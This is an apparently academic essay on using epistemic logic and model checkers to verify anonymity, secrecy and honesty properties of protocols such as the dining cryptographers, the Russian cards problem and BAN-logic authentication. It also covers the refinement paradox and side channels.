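| Cryptographers | MCMAS | MCK | MCTK |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 0.09 s | 75 s | 0.13 s |
| 20 | 0.67 s | 47,937 s | 35 s |
| 30 | 1.5 s | over 24 hours | 2.9 s |
| 50 | 13 s | over 24 hours | 72 s |
| 60 | 14 s | over 24 hours | over 24 hours |

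MCMAS wins easily, but its own developers ran the test, and it covers a single protocol. The times also depend on more than the size of the problem. MCTK needed 35 seconds for 20 cryptographers and only 3 for 30, probably because the checkers reorder their variables as they go and sometimes find a good order by luck. MCK's times also predate van der Meyden's variable-removal step, which made it far faster on this protocol. (Lomuscio and colleagues also report a run with 250 cryptographers, but the formula there contains no knowledge operator, so it is not a result about anonymity.)

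### What checking revealed about anonymous broadcast

Chaum's two-phase protocol lets several people send messages in the same session. With three participants and three time slots, it takes six rounds of the dining cryptographers protocol. The participants reserve slots in the first three rounds and send their messages in the last three, one bit per slot. Someone who wants slot 2 flips her announcement in round 2. The result of each round is the XOR of what the participants put in.

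If two people request the same slot, the reservation round gives 0 and both of them see that there is a conflict. If three people request it, the round gives 1, just as if only one had. The designers of Herbivore, which uses this protocol, wrote that a collision of this kind would occur in the transmission phase. Al-Bataineh and van der Meyden used MCK to check whether participants always find out about a conflict, and it produced a counterexample in which all three request slot 2 and all three want to send a 1:

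| Who requests slot 2, with bit 1 | Reservation result | Transmission result |
|---|---|---|
| all three participants | 1 ⊕ 1 ⊕ 1 = 1 | 1 ⊕ 1 ⊕ 1 = 1 |
| only participant 1 | 1 ⊕ 0 ⊕ 0 = 1 | 1 ⊕ 0 ⊕ 0 = 1 |

Participant 1 can't distinguish the two cases. Chaum had already noted that an odd number of identical messages can collide undetected. Herbivore adds a checksum to each message, which exposes most collisions between different messages but not collisions of this kind.

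In other counterexamples, participants learned more than Al-Bataineh and van der Meyden expected. Suppose all three reserve slot 1 and send 1, 1 and 0, so that the result is 0. Participant 1 sent a 1, so she knows that someone else also reserved the slot. Since the reservation round gave 1, an odd number of people requested the slot, so both of the others must have. Their two bits XOR to 1, so she learns from the failed transmission that one of them sent a 1 and the other a 0.

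These cases came up because Al-Bataineh and van der Meyden had written the protocol as a *knowledge-based program*, in which instructions can depend on what an agent knows. For example, one instruction is to send your bit unless you know that someone else has requested your slot. A computer can't run such an instruction directly, so they guessed an equivalent test on the results of the rounds. They then used MCK to search for situations where the test didn't match what the agent knew, and revised the test until there were none left. Huang and van der Meyden later automated the search for equivalent tests.

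If all three participants successfully send a 1, each of them knows what the others sent, and no protocol can prevent that. The anonymity formula therefore requires that each participant either knows that all the others have the same bit or does not know any of their bits. MCK verified this formula for three participants.

For larger groups the model had to become simpler. In a companion paper, Al-Bataineh and van der Meyden (2010), in *Abstraction for Epistemic Model Checking of Dining Cryptographers-based Protocols*, replaced each round with an imaginary trusted party who privately collects everyone's bit and announces only the XOR. They proved by hand that this changes no participant's knowledge of anything outside the workings of the rounds, including knowledge about what other participants know. MCK could then check anonymity in the simpler model:

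| Participants | Rounds | Full protocol | With the trusted party |
|---|---|---|---|
| 3 | 5 | 335 s | 3.1 s |
| 3 | 6 | 7,350 s | 17.8 s |
| 4 | 8 | out of memory | 249 s |
| 5 | 10 | out of memory | 1,990 s |

Anonymity held for three, four and five participants. Checking the larger models also settled whether a participant should send unless she knows that somebody else has requested her slot, or more cautiously, only if she *knows* that nobody else has. With five participants and five slots, there is no conflict if at least four of the reservation results are 1, because at least four different people must have requested those slots and a fifth could not have joined any of them without turning its result into 0. With fewer 1s, a participant whose reservation seems to have succeeded generally can't rule out a three-way collision. A cautious participant would therefore send only when nearly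 everyone has a message and they all happen to choose different slots.

### Seven cards and three checkers

The Russian cards problem comes from the 2000 Moscow Mathematical Olympiad. Anne and Bill each draw three cards from a pack of seven, numbered 0 to 6, and Cath gets the last one. Anne and Bill want to tell each other their hands by speaking aloud, without Cath learning who holds any of the other six cards.

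Suppose Anne holds cards 0, 1 and 2, Bill holds 3, 4 and 5, and Cath holds 6. Anne can say, "My hand is one of 012, 034, 056, 135 and 246." Bill holds a card from every hand on the list except 012, so he knows Anne's hand. Cath can rule out only 056 and 246. Each card from 0 to 5 appears in at least one of the other three hands and is missing from at least one, so she can't tell who holds any of them. Bill then says that Cath has card 6. Anne now knows his hand too, and Cath learns nothing new.

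*Model Checking Russian Cards* (van Ditmarsch, van der Hoek et al., 2005) verified this solution in MCK, MCMAS and DEMO. DEMO is a checker for logics in which announcements change what agents know. There are 140 possible deals, and no check took more than a few minutes. The paper compared the effort of modelling in each tool rather than the tools' speed. An expert in DEMO needed about half a day to write the model, and an expert in MCK needed about the same for a first version. The MCMAS input was thousands of lines long and had to be generated automatically, while the MCK input was about a hundred lines.

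Working out what to check was harder. Suppose Anne says instead, "I have 012, or I have none of those cards." Cath, who has 6, seems to be left with two possible hands for Anne, 012 and 345. But if Anne had 345, then for all Anne knew, Cath might hold card 0. Cath would then learn from the announcement that Anne did not have 012, and so that Bill had cards 1 and 2. So if Cath knows that Anne only makes announcements she considers safe, Cath can conclude that Anne has 012.

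Van Ditmarsch and colleagues therefore require both that Cath is ignorant just after the announcement and that her ignorance is common knowledge among all three players, so that nobody can learn anything further from it. At the time, MCK could not express common knowledge under perfect recall, so the researchers checked that the properties held in every deal consistent with the announcements, which is enough to make those properties common knowledge.

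### Checking the odds

None of these checks would detect a biased coin, because they test only what an observer considers possible. *Symbolic Model Checking of Probabilistic Knowledge* (Huang, Luo and van der Meyden, 2011) extended MCK to fix this. The user gives each random choice a weight, and a formula can then refer to the probability an agent assigns to a fact, given everything the agent has observed.

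They tested four grades of anonymity on the dining cryptographers, including probable innocence and conditional anonymity. *Possible innocence* requires the observer's probability that the payer paid to stay below some high limit, here 0.9. Under *beyond suspicion*, the payer must seem no more likely to have paid than any other candidate. For four cryptographers with fair coins, they varied how likely cryptographer 1 was to pay, compared with each of the others and with nobody at the table paying:

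| Odds for cryptographer 1 | Probability after the protocol | Possible innocence | Probable innocence | Beyond suspicion | Conditional anonymity |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 to 1 | 0.33 | holds | holds | holds | holds |
| 2 to 1 | 0.5 | holds | holds | fails | holds |
| 3 to 1 | 0.6 | holds | fails | fails | holds |
| 19 to 1 | 0.905 | fails | fails | fails | holds |

A colleague who did not pay assigns this probability to cryptographer 1 having paid, once she learns that someone at the table paid. With odds of 3 to 1, it is 3/(3 + 1 + 1) = 0.6. Conditional anonymity holds throughout, because the suspicions existed before the protocol ran. With coins that land on one side 11 times out of 12, all four grades of anonymity fail.

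Probabilities slow the checker down more for some protocols than for others. For the dining cryptographers, the running time grew faster with probabilities than without, and the experiments stopped at six cryptographers. For oblivious transfer with messages of up to 35 bits, probabilities made little difference. PRISM can also calculate probabilities, but its user has to write a separate formula for each sequence of observations an agent might make, while MCK covers all the sequences at once.

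### Mostly a success at definitions

The case studies on key establishment are the closest to everyday security practice. Boureanu and colleagues ran their compiler on protocols from two public collections and checked the output with MCMAS. According to Lomuscio and colleagues, the checks confirmed known bugs in some of the protocols and verified others, at speeds comparable to those of the best model checkers for security protocols. Finding known bugs is a good test of the method, but it gives protocol designers little reason to switch from a tool that already finds them.

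Pucella's judgment that epistemic logic has contributed more to definitions than to verification seems fair on this record. He attributes this mainly to claims about knowledge being hard to check, which is why practical tools often replace them with claims that are easier to check, such as safety properties. He writes that by 2013 many methods could check confidentiality and authentication against a Dolev–Yao attacker quite efficiently, using definitions close to the epistemic ones.

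### Looking for a bad state

Three of the best-known protocol tools are ProVerif (introduced by Bruno Blanchet in 2001), Tamarin (2012) and DeepSec (2018). None of them requires the user to write the knowledge operator K.

To verify secrecy of keys and authentication, ProVerif and Tamarin check *reachability*, which means whether any run leads to a bad state, such as one where the attacker has the key or one where Bob has finished a session with Alice that she never started. This is enough for simple goals. "The attacker never has message knowledge of the key" is already a claim about single states. In "when Bob finishes, he knows that Alice took part", the words "he knows that" are redundant, like the outer K in the compiler's formulas.

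In return, the tools can cover an unlimited number of sessions, whereas MCK and MCMAS need a finite model. ProVerif translates a protocol into rules about what the attacker can derive. The translation can overestimate the attacker, so ProVerif sometimes reports an attack that is not real. It also sometimes never finishes. But when it proves a key stays secret, the proof holds for any number of sessions. Tamarin works backwards from the bad state and tries to construct a run that leads to it. It may not finish either, but the user can help by supplying intermediate steps.

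This has made it possible to analyse protocols that billions of devices use. In *A Formal Analysis of 5G Authentication*, Basin, Dreier and colleagues (2018) applied Tamarin to the protocol that authenticates phones on 5G networks. They found that it met some critical security goals only with added assumptions that were not in the standard. None of the epistemic case studies above analyses a deployed protocol of that size.

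### When two processes look the same

Reachability can't express anonymity, because no single state shows that an observer has identified the payer. For such properties, the tools compare two versions of the protocol, for example one in which cryptographer 2 pays and one in which cryptographer 3 does. The versions are *trace equivalent* if, for every run of either version, the other has a run that looks the same to the observer.

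In a system that contains the runs of both versions and gives cryptographer 1 perfect recall, the versions are trace equivalent if and only if she never knows whether cryptographer 2 or 3 paid. If they are trace equivalent, then at every point where 2 paid, she also considers it possible that 3 did, and vice versa, so she never knows which of them paid. Conversely, if she never knows which of them paid, then whatever she observes in one version she could also have observed in the other, so the versions are trace equivalent.

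They agree because three conditions hold:

- The tool and the logic use the same definition of when two observations look alike. With encryption, this means that the attacker cannot compute any test that separates them.
- The observer remembers everything.
- The system contains only the two alternatives.

With more alternatives, the two can differ. The program that prints whether a secret digit is even never lets the observer know the digit, but the versions with 3 and 4 are not equivalent, because they print different things. Requiring every pair of versions to be equivalent amounts to noninterference.

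The user therefore has to choose the pair carefully. In an election, a version where Alice votes for x is not equivalent to one where she votes for y, because the published tally changes. The usual test for vote privacy has Alice and Bob swap votes, which leaves the tally unchanged.

The tools also differ in what they prove. For this kind of property, ProVerif and Tamarin normally check a stricter relation than trace equivalence, in which the two versions have the same structure and must take matching steps throughout. If this relation holds, the versions are trace equivalent, but it can fail even when the protocol keeps its secret. DeepSec decides trace equivalence directly, but only for a fixed number of sessions.

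Comparing two versions can also be simpler than writing a formula. To say in epistemic logic that an observer learns nothing, one has to say, for every suitable φ, that the observer does not know φ. Pucella calls this clunkier than the direct comparison, and he sees no real demand for an explicit logic of knowledge in research on noninterference. He suggests that such a logic might be more useful where a system is meant to release some information but not all of it.

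### The case for writing the K

Defenders of epistemic specifications reply that such specifications are easier to understand. Lomuscio and colleagues argue that security analysts think in terms of what the participants know, so formulas about knowledge match what they mean. For example, "She knows that one of them paid and does not know which" is easier to compare with Chaum's story than a pair of processes is. But the advantage is modest, since a formula about knowledge can also leave out half of what its author intended.

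Requirements about what one participant knows of another's knowledge are the better argument for this approach. In the broadcast protocol, Al-Bataineh and van der Meyden let a sender stop resending her bit once she knows that every other participant knows that someone is sending that bit. The requirement on Cath's ignorance is nested in the same way, as is the authentication goal that Boureanu and colleagues found to hold with one level of knowledge but not with two. None of these conditions can be expressed simply as avoiding a bad state or as comparing one pair of processes. Most security goals have no such nesting, which helps to explain why the simpler tools are usually enough.

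### Between the two approaches

Some recent methods still check statements about knowledge but use other kinds of software to do it. *Program Semantics and Verification Technique for AI-Centred Programs* (Rajaona, Boureanu and colleagues, 2023) uses a *program epistemic logic*, which describes what agents know before and after a program runs. Its method translates formulas of this logic into ordinary first-order logic and passes the result to an automatic solver.

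In the translation, "the observer knows φ" becomes "φ holds for all values of the hidden variables that fit what the observer sees". Suppose the program above has just printed "even". The claim that the observer knows the digit is 4 becomes

```
for every digit d:  if d is even, then d = 4
```

The solver refutes this with d = 2. It works on formulas rather than a table of states, so the variables can range over all the integers, which a finite model does not allow.

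*Alpha-Beta Privacy* (Mödersheim and Viganò, 2019) defines privacy without requiring the analyst to choose pairs of processes. The analyst writes a formula α that describes what the protocol deliberately reveals. In an election with three voters, α might say that each vote is 0 or 1 and that the votes add up to 2. A second formula, β, describes everything the attacker has: the messages it has seen, how the protocol works, and α itself. Privacy holds if β rules out none of the combinations of votes that α allows, which here are (1, 1, 0), (1, 0, 1) and (0, 1, 1). If α instead says that the votes add up to 3, it allows only (1, 1, 1), so the attacker may know everyone's vote without any violation of privacy.

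This is an ignorance claim that specifies the permitted leaks. It can be checked one state at a time because β records the attacker's uncertainty in each state. Privacy then becomes a reachability problem again, namely whether the protocol can reach a state where β reveals more than α. *A Decision Procedure for Alpha-Beta Privacy for a Bounded Number of Transitions* (Fernet, Mödersheim and Viganò, 2024) gives an algorithm that answers this for runs up to a fixed length.

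Other researchers have built the comparison of runs into the logic itself. HyperLTL, which Clarkson, Finkbeiner and colleagues (2014) introduced in *Temporal Logics for Hyperproperties*, has variables that stand for whole runs. In words, cryptographer 2's anonymity towards cryptographer 1 then looks like this:

```
for every run r in which 2 paid, there is a run r' in which 3 paid
and cryptographer 1 observes the same things in r' as in r
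```

A HyperLTL formula can refer to only a fixed number of runs, so it cannot express common knowledge, which involves chains of "she knows that he knows" of any length. *Second-Order Hyperproperties* (Beutner, Finkbeiner and colleagues, 2023) therefore extends the logic with variables for sets of runs. No algorithm can check every formula of the extended logic, so the paper's tool, HySO, handles a restricted part of it by approximating the sets from above and below.

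## What does a verified "does not know" depend on?

The dining cryptographers protocol passes its anonymity check because, for every run in which cryptographer 2 paid, there is a run in which cryptographer 3 paid that looks the same to cryptographer 1. If a change to the model removes one run of such a pair, or lets cryptographer 1 tell the two apart, the result no longer holds.

### Changing one choice at a time

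Suppose a mirror behind the other two lets cryptographer 1 see c23, the coin they tossed without her. This adds one name to her "observes" line in the checker's input but leaves the protocol and its 32 runs unchanged. The two runs in each of the 8 pairs differ in c23, so she can now tell them apart and always knows who paid.

If the mirror is removed and any number of cryptographers can pay, there are 8 combinations of payers and 8 ways for the coins to land, which makes 64 runs. Cryptographer 1 did not pay in 32 of them, and each of her local states now occurs in two of these. Each of the 8 runs in which the NSA paid, which she could identify before, now looks the same to her as a run in which 2 and 3 both paid. She therefore never knows that nobody at the table paid, and the formula fails. Her colleagues' secrets are as safe as before, but she can no longer learn from the protocol that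 the NSA paid.

| Model | Runs in which 1 did not pay | Grouping for cryptographer 1 | Where the formula is false |
|---|---|---|---|
| Original | 24 | 8 single runs, 8 pairs | nowhere |
| 1 also sees c23 | 24 | 24 single runs | the 16 runs where 2 or 3 paid |
| Any number may pay | 32 | 16 pairs | the 16 runs where neither or both of 2 and 3 paid |
| c23 always lands 0 | 12 | 12 single runs | the 8 runs where 2 or 3 paid |

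Another assumption, that the cryptographers don't share what they know, is easier to overlook because the formula stays true without it. The formula covers only what cryptographer 1 knows, so a checker would still pass it if she and cryptographer 3 planned to compare notes after dinner. To cover that case, the analyst has to check what the two would know if they pooled their information (their distributed knowledge), which includes whether cryptographer 2 paid.

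Adding diners does not necessarily make anonymity stronger. If 100 diners sit in a ring and each shares coins only with her two neighbours, those neighbours together know both of her coins and can work out whether she paid without help from the other 97.

A verified "does not know" also depends on what the participants know beforehand. Al-Bataineh and van der Meyden ask whether the flow of information changes when Chaum's two-phase protocol is used for a referendum, where everyone knows that all the participants will try to reserve a slot. A small example shows that it can. Suppose three participants share three slots, and the reservation results are 1, 0 and 0. The participant who requested the first slot would normally think she might be the only one with something to send. If she knows that all three requested a slot, she also knows that at least two of them collided, because requests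 for three different slots would have given 1, 1 and 1.

Al-Bataineh and van der Meyden acknowledge that their results do not show what would happen with more agents, a different arrangement of coins or other initial assumptions. The advantage of a model checker is that an analyst can change the input and rerun the checker without rebuilding a proof.

### Fewer runs, more knowledge

The table shows the formula failing for opposite reasons. K_i φ means that φ is true at every point that looks the same to agent i as the current one. Removing runs can therefore create knowledge by eliminating the last such point where φ was false, while adding runs can destroy knowledge by introducing a point where φ is false.

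If φ is a plain fact, with no K inside it, a true claim that an agent knows φ stays true when other runs are removed, and a true claim that the agent does not know φ stays true when other runs are added. The anonymity formula requires both knowledge and ignorance, so either removing or adding runs can make it false.

This is a problem for anyone who turns a model into software. A model usually leaves some choices open for programmers to settle. In the standard sense, a program *refines* a specification if the specification allows everything the program can do.

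Suppose a programmer replaces "random bit" with 0 for all three coins. Only 4 of the 32 runs remain, one for each possible payer. The specification allows all four, and the XOR of the announcements still correctly shows whether a cryptographer paid. But each announcement is now a1 = p1, a2 = p2 or a3 = p3, so a cryptographer who paid says 1 and the others say 0, and even the stranger at the next table can see who paid.

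The diners might not realise that the coins are stuck, but under the definition they still count as knowing it, just as Bob counted as knowing Alice's habit. This is sensible for a security claim, since an attacker may have read the program.

Jeremy Jacob's *On shared systems* (1987) examined when one shared computer system can replace another and how much information flows through such a system. According to *Formal approaches to information hiding* (2011), Jacob showed in a 1989 paper that a consistent refinement of a specification can lack the specification's security properties. Researchers call this the *refinement paradox*.

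A design choice that looks harmless can cause the leak. Mantel (2001), in *Preserving Information Flow Properties under Refinement*, gives an example with two visible events and one hidden event, each of which can happen at most once, in any order. A designer then decides that one of the visible events can happen only after at least one of the other two. An observer who sees that event before the other visible one now knows that the hidden event has already happened.

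Schedulers, which decide what runs next in a concurrent system, can cause the same problem. Suppose a model of the dining cryptographers didn't specify who announces first, and the software always had the payer go first. The order of the announcements would then reveal who paid, even though the announcements were perfectly encrypted.

### Refinements that preserve ignorance

One remedy is to check secrecy again after every design step, but Mantel considers this too much work. Checking only the finished design is not much better, because fixing a leak that late may make the system useless. He instead offers operations that adjust a refinement so that it keeps the secret. The designer lists the steps to forbid, and the operation either forbids more steps or allows some of those listed. In his example, the operation could make the delayed event wait for the other visible event whether or not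 the hidden one has happened, so that seeing the delayed event would reveal nothing about the hidden one.

Morgan, in *The Shadow Knows*, changed the definition of refinement itself. In the simplest version of his model, a program has a visible variable v and a hidden variable h, and there is one observer. He adds a third variable H, the *shadow*, which is the set of values that h could have as far as the observer can tell. A three-step program shows how it works:

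| Instruction | What the observer sees in v | Shadow H afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| set h to any of 0, 1, 2, 3 | nothing new | {0, 1, 2, 3} |
| set v to the remainder of h divided by 2 | 0 or 1 | {0, 2} or {1, 3} |
| set v to 0 | 0 | the same as before |

The last instruction overwrites the evidence, but the shadow stays small because the observer has perfect recall.

Under Morgan's definition, each outcome of the new program must match an outcome of the old one with the same v and the same h, and the new shadow must contain the old one, so the observer's uncertainty may grow but not shrink. Replacing a hidden random bit with 0 fails this test because the shadow shrinks from {0, 1} to {0}.

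Morgan had to show that his definition still permits useful refinements, because a definition that forbade every refinement would also prevent leaks. He starts from a one-line specification that publishes only p1 ⊕ p2 ⊕ p3 and transforms it step by step into the dining cryptographers protocol. The main step introduces a hidden random key and publishes a secret combined with that key. This reveals nothing if, for any message that might appear, every possible secret could have produced it with some key. XORing a one-bit secret with one coin flip meets this condition.

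Morgan also gives a flawed version of the protocol, which computes the right answer but can reveal whether a particular cryptographer paid. Each cryptographer treats her coins as ordinary numbers. She takes one coin, adds 1 if she paid, and subtracts the other coin. When everyone's results are added up, each coin is added once and subtracted once, so the coins cancel and the total is odd exactly when a cryptographer paid. But if her coins are 1 and 0 and she paid, she announces 1 + 1 − 0 = 2. Only a cryptographer who paid can announce 2, so this reveals that she paid. Similarly, an announcement of −1 proves that the speaker did not pay. Morgan's refinement rejects this version, although ordinary refinement accepts it.

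Morgan's method shows that a program reveals no more than its specification does. The specification here must reveal something, because the protocol is supposed to reveal whether a cryptographer paid. The method handles only one observer at a time, and the 2006 version does not cover loops. It also does not cover probabilities, so a protocol that used a biased coin would pass.

Later work extended the approach. *The thousand-and-one cryptographers* (McIver and Morgan, 2009) used refinement to prove the protocol correct for any number of diners. *Security Engineering in IIIf, Part II* (Kammüller, 2024) brought a solution to the refinement paradox into a security framework for the proof assistant Isabelle.

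Difficulties remain when a refinement also changes how a program represents its data or what an observer can see. *On compositional information flow aware refinement* points out that refining the successive parts of a program separately then no longer guarantees that the whole is safe. To fix this, it proposes extra conditions relating the two versions of the program before and after each part. Refinement can also introduce secrets that are not in the specification, such as the coins here, and these need their own protection.

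### From private channels to encrypted messages

Some changes preserve both what agents know and what they don't. In *Preservation of Epistemic Properties in Security Protocol Implementations* (2007), van der Meyden and Wilke proved this for a common one. The idealised protocol lets agents send messages over private channels. In the implementation, the sender instead encrypts the message with a fresh key and broadcasts it to everyone.

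Suppose the cryptographers are in different cities. Cryptographer 1 tosses coin c12 and has to tell 2 the result without letting 3 find out. If 1 and 2 already share a random key bit k, then 1 can broadcast c12 ⊕ k. This is one-time pad encryption, so 3 learns nothing about the coin from the broadcast.

The theorem covers every formula of their logic about the original protocol's variables, including formulas about what one agent knows of another's knowledge. Such a formula is true of the idealised protocol if and only if it is true of the implementation, provided the cipher is good enough. There are two versions of this requirement:

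- If the formula does not mention probabilities, every message must be able to produce every ciphertext that any other message can produce, given a suitable key. This is the same condition that Morgan needs for his main step.
- If the formula does mention probabilities, every message must also be equally likely to produce a given ciphertext. This is Claude Shannon's *perfect secrecy*.

The proof works because it matches situations in both directions. If two situations look the same to an agent in the implementation, the corresponding ones must look the same in the idealised protocol, so the agent gains no new uncertainty. If the agent considers a situation possible in the idealised protocol, the implementation must contain a matching situation that the agent still considers possible. The stuck coins fail the second requirement because the alternative payer has no matching run.

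The theorem has a practical drawback, because the keys must first be sent over a private channel. For a single coin, the only gain is that the private contact can happen in advance. Van der Meyden and Wilke also assume that attackers only listen, and they do not consider how hard a cipher is to break. Most everyday encryption uses a short key for a lot of data and relies on attackers' limited computing power, so their result does not apply to it.

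The step from model to code is easier for properties of single runs. *Sound Verification of Security Protocols* (2022) describes a method that translates a Tamarin model into a specification of what each participant's program may send and receive, and then verifies the program against it. Every single-run property proved for the model also holds for the verified code. This does not cover anonymity, which depends on how runs compare.

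### Timing and other omitted observations

Even a program that matches its model exactly can leak, because people and machines may observe things the model leaves out. Suppose the payer takes slightly longer to work out her announcement because she has to reverse it. Anyone who timed the announcements could then identify her. Adding this delay to what cryptographer 1 observes in the model would have the same effect as showing cryptographer 1 c23, and all 8 pairs would split.

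MCK would not detect this delay unless the user modelled it, because all agents in MCK move in lock-step, one action per tick. In their study of the two-phase protocol, Al-Bataineh and van der Meyden also treat "if" tests as taking no time. Their program tests whether the current slot is the one the participant requested, and sends her message only if it is. On a real computer, the two cases might take different amounts of time, which would show who was sending.

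Morgan assumes the opposite, that the observer sees which instructions the program executes. This changes the result for a program that follows Chaum's story literally ("if I paid, announce the opposite of what I see, otherwise announce what I see"), because an observer who sees which branch the program takes learns whether the speaker paid. A program that computes paid ⊕ coin ⊕ coin in one step gives the same announcements without that leak. Which assumption fits depends on the equipment and on how close the attacker can get to it.

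A proof can leave out parts of the protocol as well as physical details. Chaum's proof covers a single round of his protocol, and Al-Bataineh and van der Meyden found that the way rounds are combined can leak information. In their example of a failed transmission with three participants in one slot, participant 1 had to combine the results of two rounds to learn that one of the others had sent a 1 and the other a 0. The leak is small, since she still can't tell who sent which, and their anonymity formula allows it. But it comes from a connection between rounds, which a proof about one round could not examine.

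Modellers can easily represent a side channel in this framework by adding a variable for the delay, sound or power consumption and declaring who can observe it. But they have to think of the channel first, because a model checker compares only the observations included in the model and cannot detect that a real observer has others.

### Four conditions that make checking possible

The results on protocols were possible because the analysts could supply four things:

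- **A written program.** People wrote the rules that each participant follows, so the checker can generate every run from them. The verdict carries over to other software only if that software preserves what each agent considers possible.
- **Declared observations.** For every agent there is a list of the variables it can see. In one of the languages that Al-Bataineh and van der Meyden use, a program may read a variable only if its agent observes it, so the list must include at least everything the program uses.
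- **A stated initial condition.** The analyst specifies which situations are possible at the start. Chaum put his in brackets, "assuming that the dinner was paid for only once", and the conclusion about the NSA depends on it.
- **An agreed attacker.** The analyst decides whose ignorance matters, whether observers may pool what they know, and whether they can interfere with messages or only listen.

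## What would an honesty claim look like in the same logic?

Secrecy and anonymity claims limit what an observer knows about someone else. An honesty claim relates what a speaker says to what she herself knows. The simplest candidate is

```
AG ( says_i φ  ⇒  K_i φ )
```

An honesty claim is that, at every moment of every run, if agent i asserts φ, then i knows φ. Fagin and Halpern (1987), in *I'm OK if You're OK*, likewise call a message honest if its sender knows it to be true when she sends it. Whatever an agent knows is true, so every honest message is true.

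In the example of the coin under the cup, Alice has looked at the coin, so she satisfies the formula if she tells Bob which side is up. If Bob says "heads" before Alice lifts the cup, he violates the formula, even in a run where the coin is heads up. He can't distinguish that run from one where the coin is tails up, so he doesn't know that the coin is heads up.

### Children who say they know

Lomuscio and colleagues used MCMAS to check a claim of this kind in a well-known puzzle. Some children in a group have mud on their foreheads. Each child reasons perfectly and sees every forehead but his own. An adult announces that at least one child is muddy, then repeatedly asks whether any child knows if he is muddy himself.

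Suppose Ann and Ben are muddy and Cal is clean. Ann sees mud on Ben and none on Cal, so either she and Ben are muddy or only Ben is. If only Ben were muddy, he would see two clean foreheads and conclude at the first question that his own was muddy. But Ben answers that he doesn't know. So when the adult asks a second time, Ann knows that she is muddy, and Ben knows that he is. In general, if k children are muddy, all k of them say so at the k-th question.

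The formula that Lomuscio and colleagues give is

```
AG ( muddy_i ∧ saysknows_i  ⇒  K_i muddy_i )
```

where saysknows_i is true after child i has said that he knows whether he is muddy. So whenever a muddy child says he knows, he does know. MCMAS checked models with up to 120 children. It needed less than a second for 20 children and between 13 and 17 minutes for 120, depending on the order in which its decision diagrams tested the variables.

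Without the K, the formula would be true of any children, because it would require only that a muddy child who says he knows is muddy.

The check tests the program that someone wrote for the children. That program could be a simple counting rule, such as "say you know at question m if you see m − 1 muddy foreheads". A child can follow the rule without reasoning about anyone's knowledge, and the checker determines whether he knows what he says he knows.

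The formula covers only one of the two answers a child can give. A child who always answered "I don't know" would satisfy it, however much he knew. To catch him, one needs a second formula:

```
AG ( saysdoesntknow_i  ⇒  ¬K_i muddy_i ∧ ¬K_i ¬muddy_i )
```

Whether a claim counts as honest also depends on when the speaker's knowledge is evaluated. Suppose Ann guesses at the first question and says she knows, although she doesn't yet. If the children answer together, she hears Ben say "I don't know" at the same moment, and from then on she knows that she is muddy. A formula evaluated only after the answers would count her claim as honest. Fagin and Halpern's definition would not, because it requires knowledge when the message is sent.

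### A logic that takes honesty for granted

BAN logic, which produced the supposed proof of the Needham–Schroeder protocol, also connects what agents say with what they believe. But it assumes the connection. In the logic of Burrows, Abadi and Needham, in *A Logic of Authentication*, "Q said X" means that Q once sent a message containing X and believed X at the time. One of the rules of inference is

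```
if    P believes that X is fresh
and   P believes that Q said X
then  P believes that Q believes X
```

X is fresh if nobody sent it before the current run of the protocol. Suppose a server sends Alice a new key k for talking to Bob. The message contains a timestamp, and the server encrypts it with a key that only it and Alice have. Alice reasons in three steps:

1. Only the server could have encrypted this, so the server said that k is a good key for her and Bob.
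2. The timestamp is recent, so the server still believes it.
3. The server is an authority on keys, so she believes it too.

The second step depends on the server's honesty. A server that sent out keys it knew to be bad would still satisfy the rule's two conditions, and Alice would draw the wrong conclusion. Burrows and colleagues accept this limit and study only the beliefs of trustworthy parties, which leaves out Isabel, the registered user who attacks Needham–Schroeder.

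Martín Abadi soon came to reject the assumption. Abadi and Tuttle (1991), in *A Semantics for a Logic of Authentication*, call it unreasonable, partly because some protocols require an agent to forward a message that she doesn't necessarily believe. For example, Alice may have to forward a ciphertext for Bob that she can't decrypt. Abadi and Tuttle therefore add a notation that marks a message as forwarded, so that an agent who uses it properly doesn't count as having said the contents.

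Their deeper objection is that honesty is not well defined in general, because whether a program is honest depends on the system it runs in. If Bob repeats whatever Alice tells him about the coin, the same program makes him honest in a system where Alice always tells the truth and dishonest in one where she sometimes lies. If Alice also relies on Bob, each one's honesty depends on the other's. Fagin and Halpern had studied conditions weaker than honesty that still guarantee true messages as long as everyone meets them. According to Abadi and Tuttle, Fagin and Halpern's definition amounts to an equation that may have no solution, or more than one.

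A model checker avoids this circle because it starts from a fixed set of runs, including any in which someone speaks falsely. BAN logic has no such set. Abadi and Tuttle fix the problem by removing honesty from the rules. In their version, if Q is an authority on X and has recently said X, then X is true, whatever Q believes. An analyst can still assume that the agents consider each other honest, but must state this as an assumption about the particular protocol.

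### What an announcement means

Checking the honesty formula requires knowing which φ each utterance asserts. This is obvious in the muddy children puzzle but less obvious in the dining cryptographers protocol, where a cryptographer who paid announces the opposite of what she sees.

Each of Chaum's cryptographers says aloud whether the two coins she sees are the same or different. If cryptographer 1's words have their ordinary English meaning, "different" means that c12 and c13 differ, and she lies in all 8 of the runs in which she paid. But the protocol defines her announcement as p1 ⊕ c12 ⊕ c13, so "different" means that this sum is 1, and she tells the truth in all 32 runs.

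The two readings also disagree about cheats. Suppose that a cryptographer cheats by announcing the opposite of what the protocol prescribes:

| Cryptographer 1 | Her announcement | Read as a report on her coins | Read as the protocol defines it |
|---|---|---|---|
| did not pay, follows the protocol | what she sees | true | true |
| paid, follows the protocol | the opposite | false | true |
| did not pay, cheats | the opposite | false | false |
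| paid, cheats | what she sees | true | false |

Someone who checked honesty with the everyday reading would accuse the payer who follows the rules and clear the one who breaks them. Enforcing that reading would also make the protocol useless, because if all three cryptographers truthfully announced whether their coins matched, the XOR of the announcements would be 0 in every run, and nobody would find out whether the NSA had paid.

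BAN logic also needs a meaning for each message, since a real message is only a string of bits. Burrows and colleagues assign these meanings by hand. For instance, they translate a ciphertext that contains a key for Alice and Bob into the statement that this key is good for communication between them. They write that they can do this only because they know how the protocol's users should understand the message. As a rough guide, they let a message stand for X if its recipient may deduce that the sender must have believed X when he sent it.

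That guide makes honesty impossible to test. If the sender turns out not to have believed X, then X counts as the wrong translation. This does no harm in a study of trustworthy parties, but an honesty check needs meanings fixed beforehand, without reference to the speaker's beliefs. Ordinary sentences rarely have such meanings. For example, "I couldn't get the test to run" might mean that the test cannot run, or only that the speaker tried for a while and stopped.

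### When crediting too much knowledge stops being safe

A secrecy claim has the form ¬K_j φ for an observer j. For such a claim, logical omniscience is usually a safe error because at worst it causes a false alarm.

The honesty formula requires the speaker to know what she asserts, whereas secrecy and anonymity require an adversary not to know something. The more knowledge the definition of K gives the speaker, the more easily she passes.

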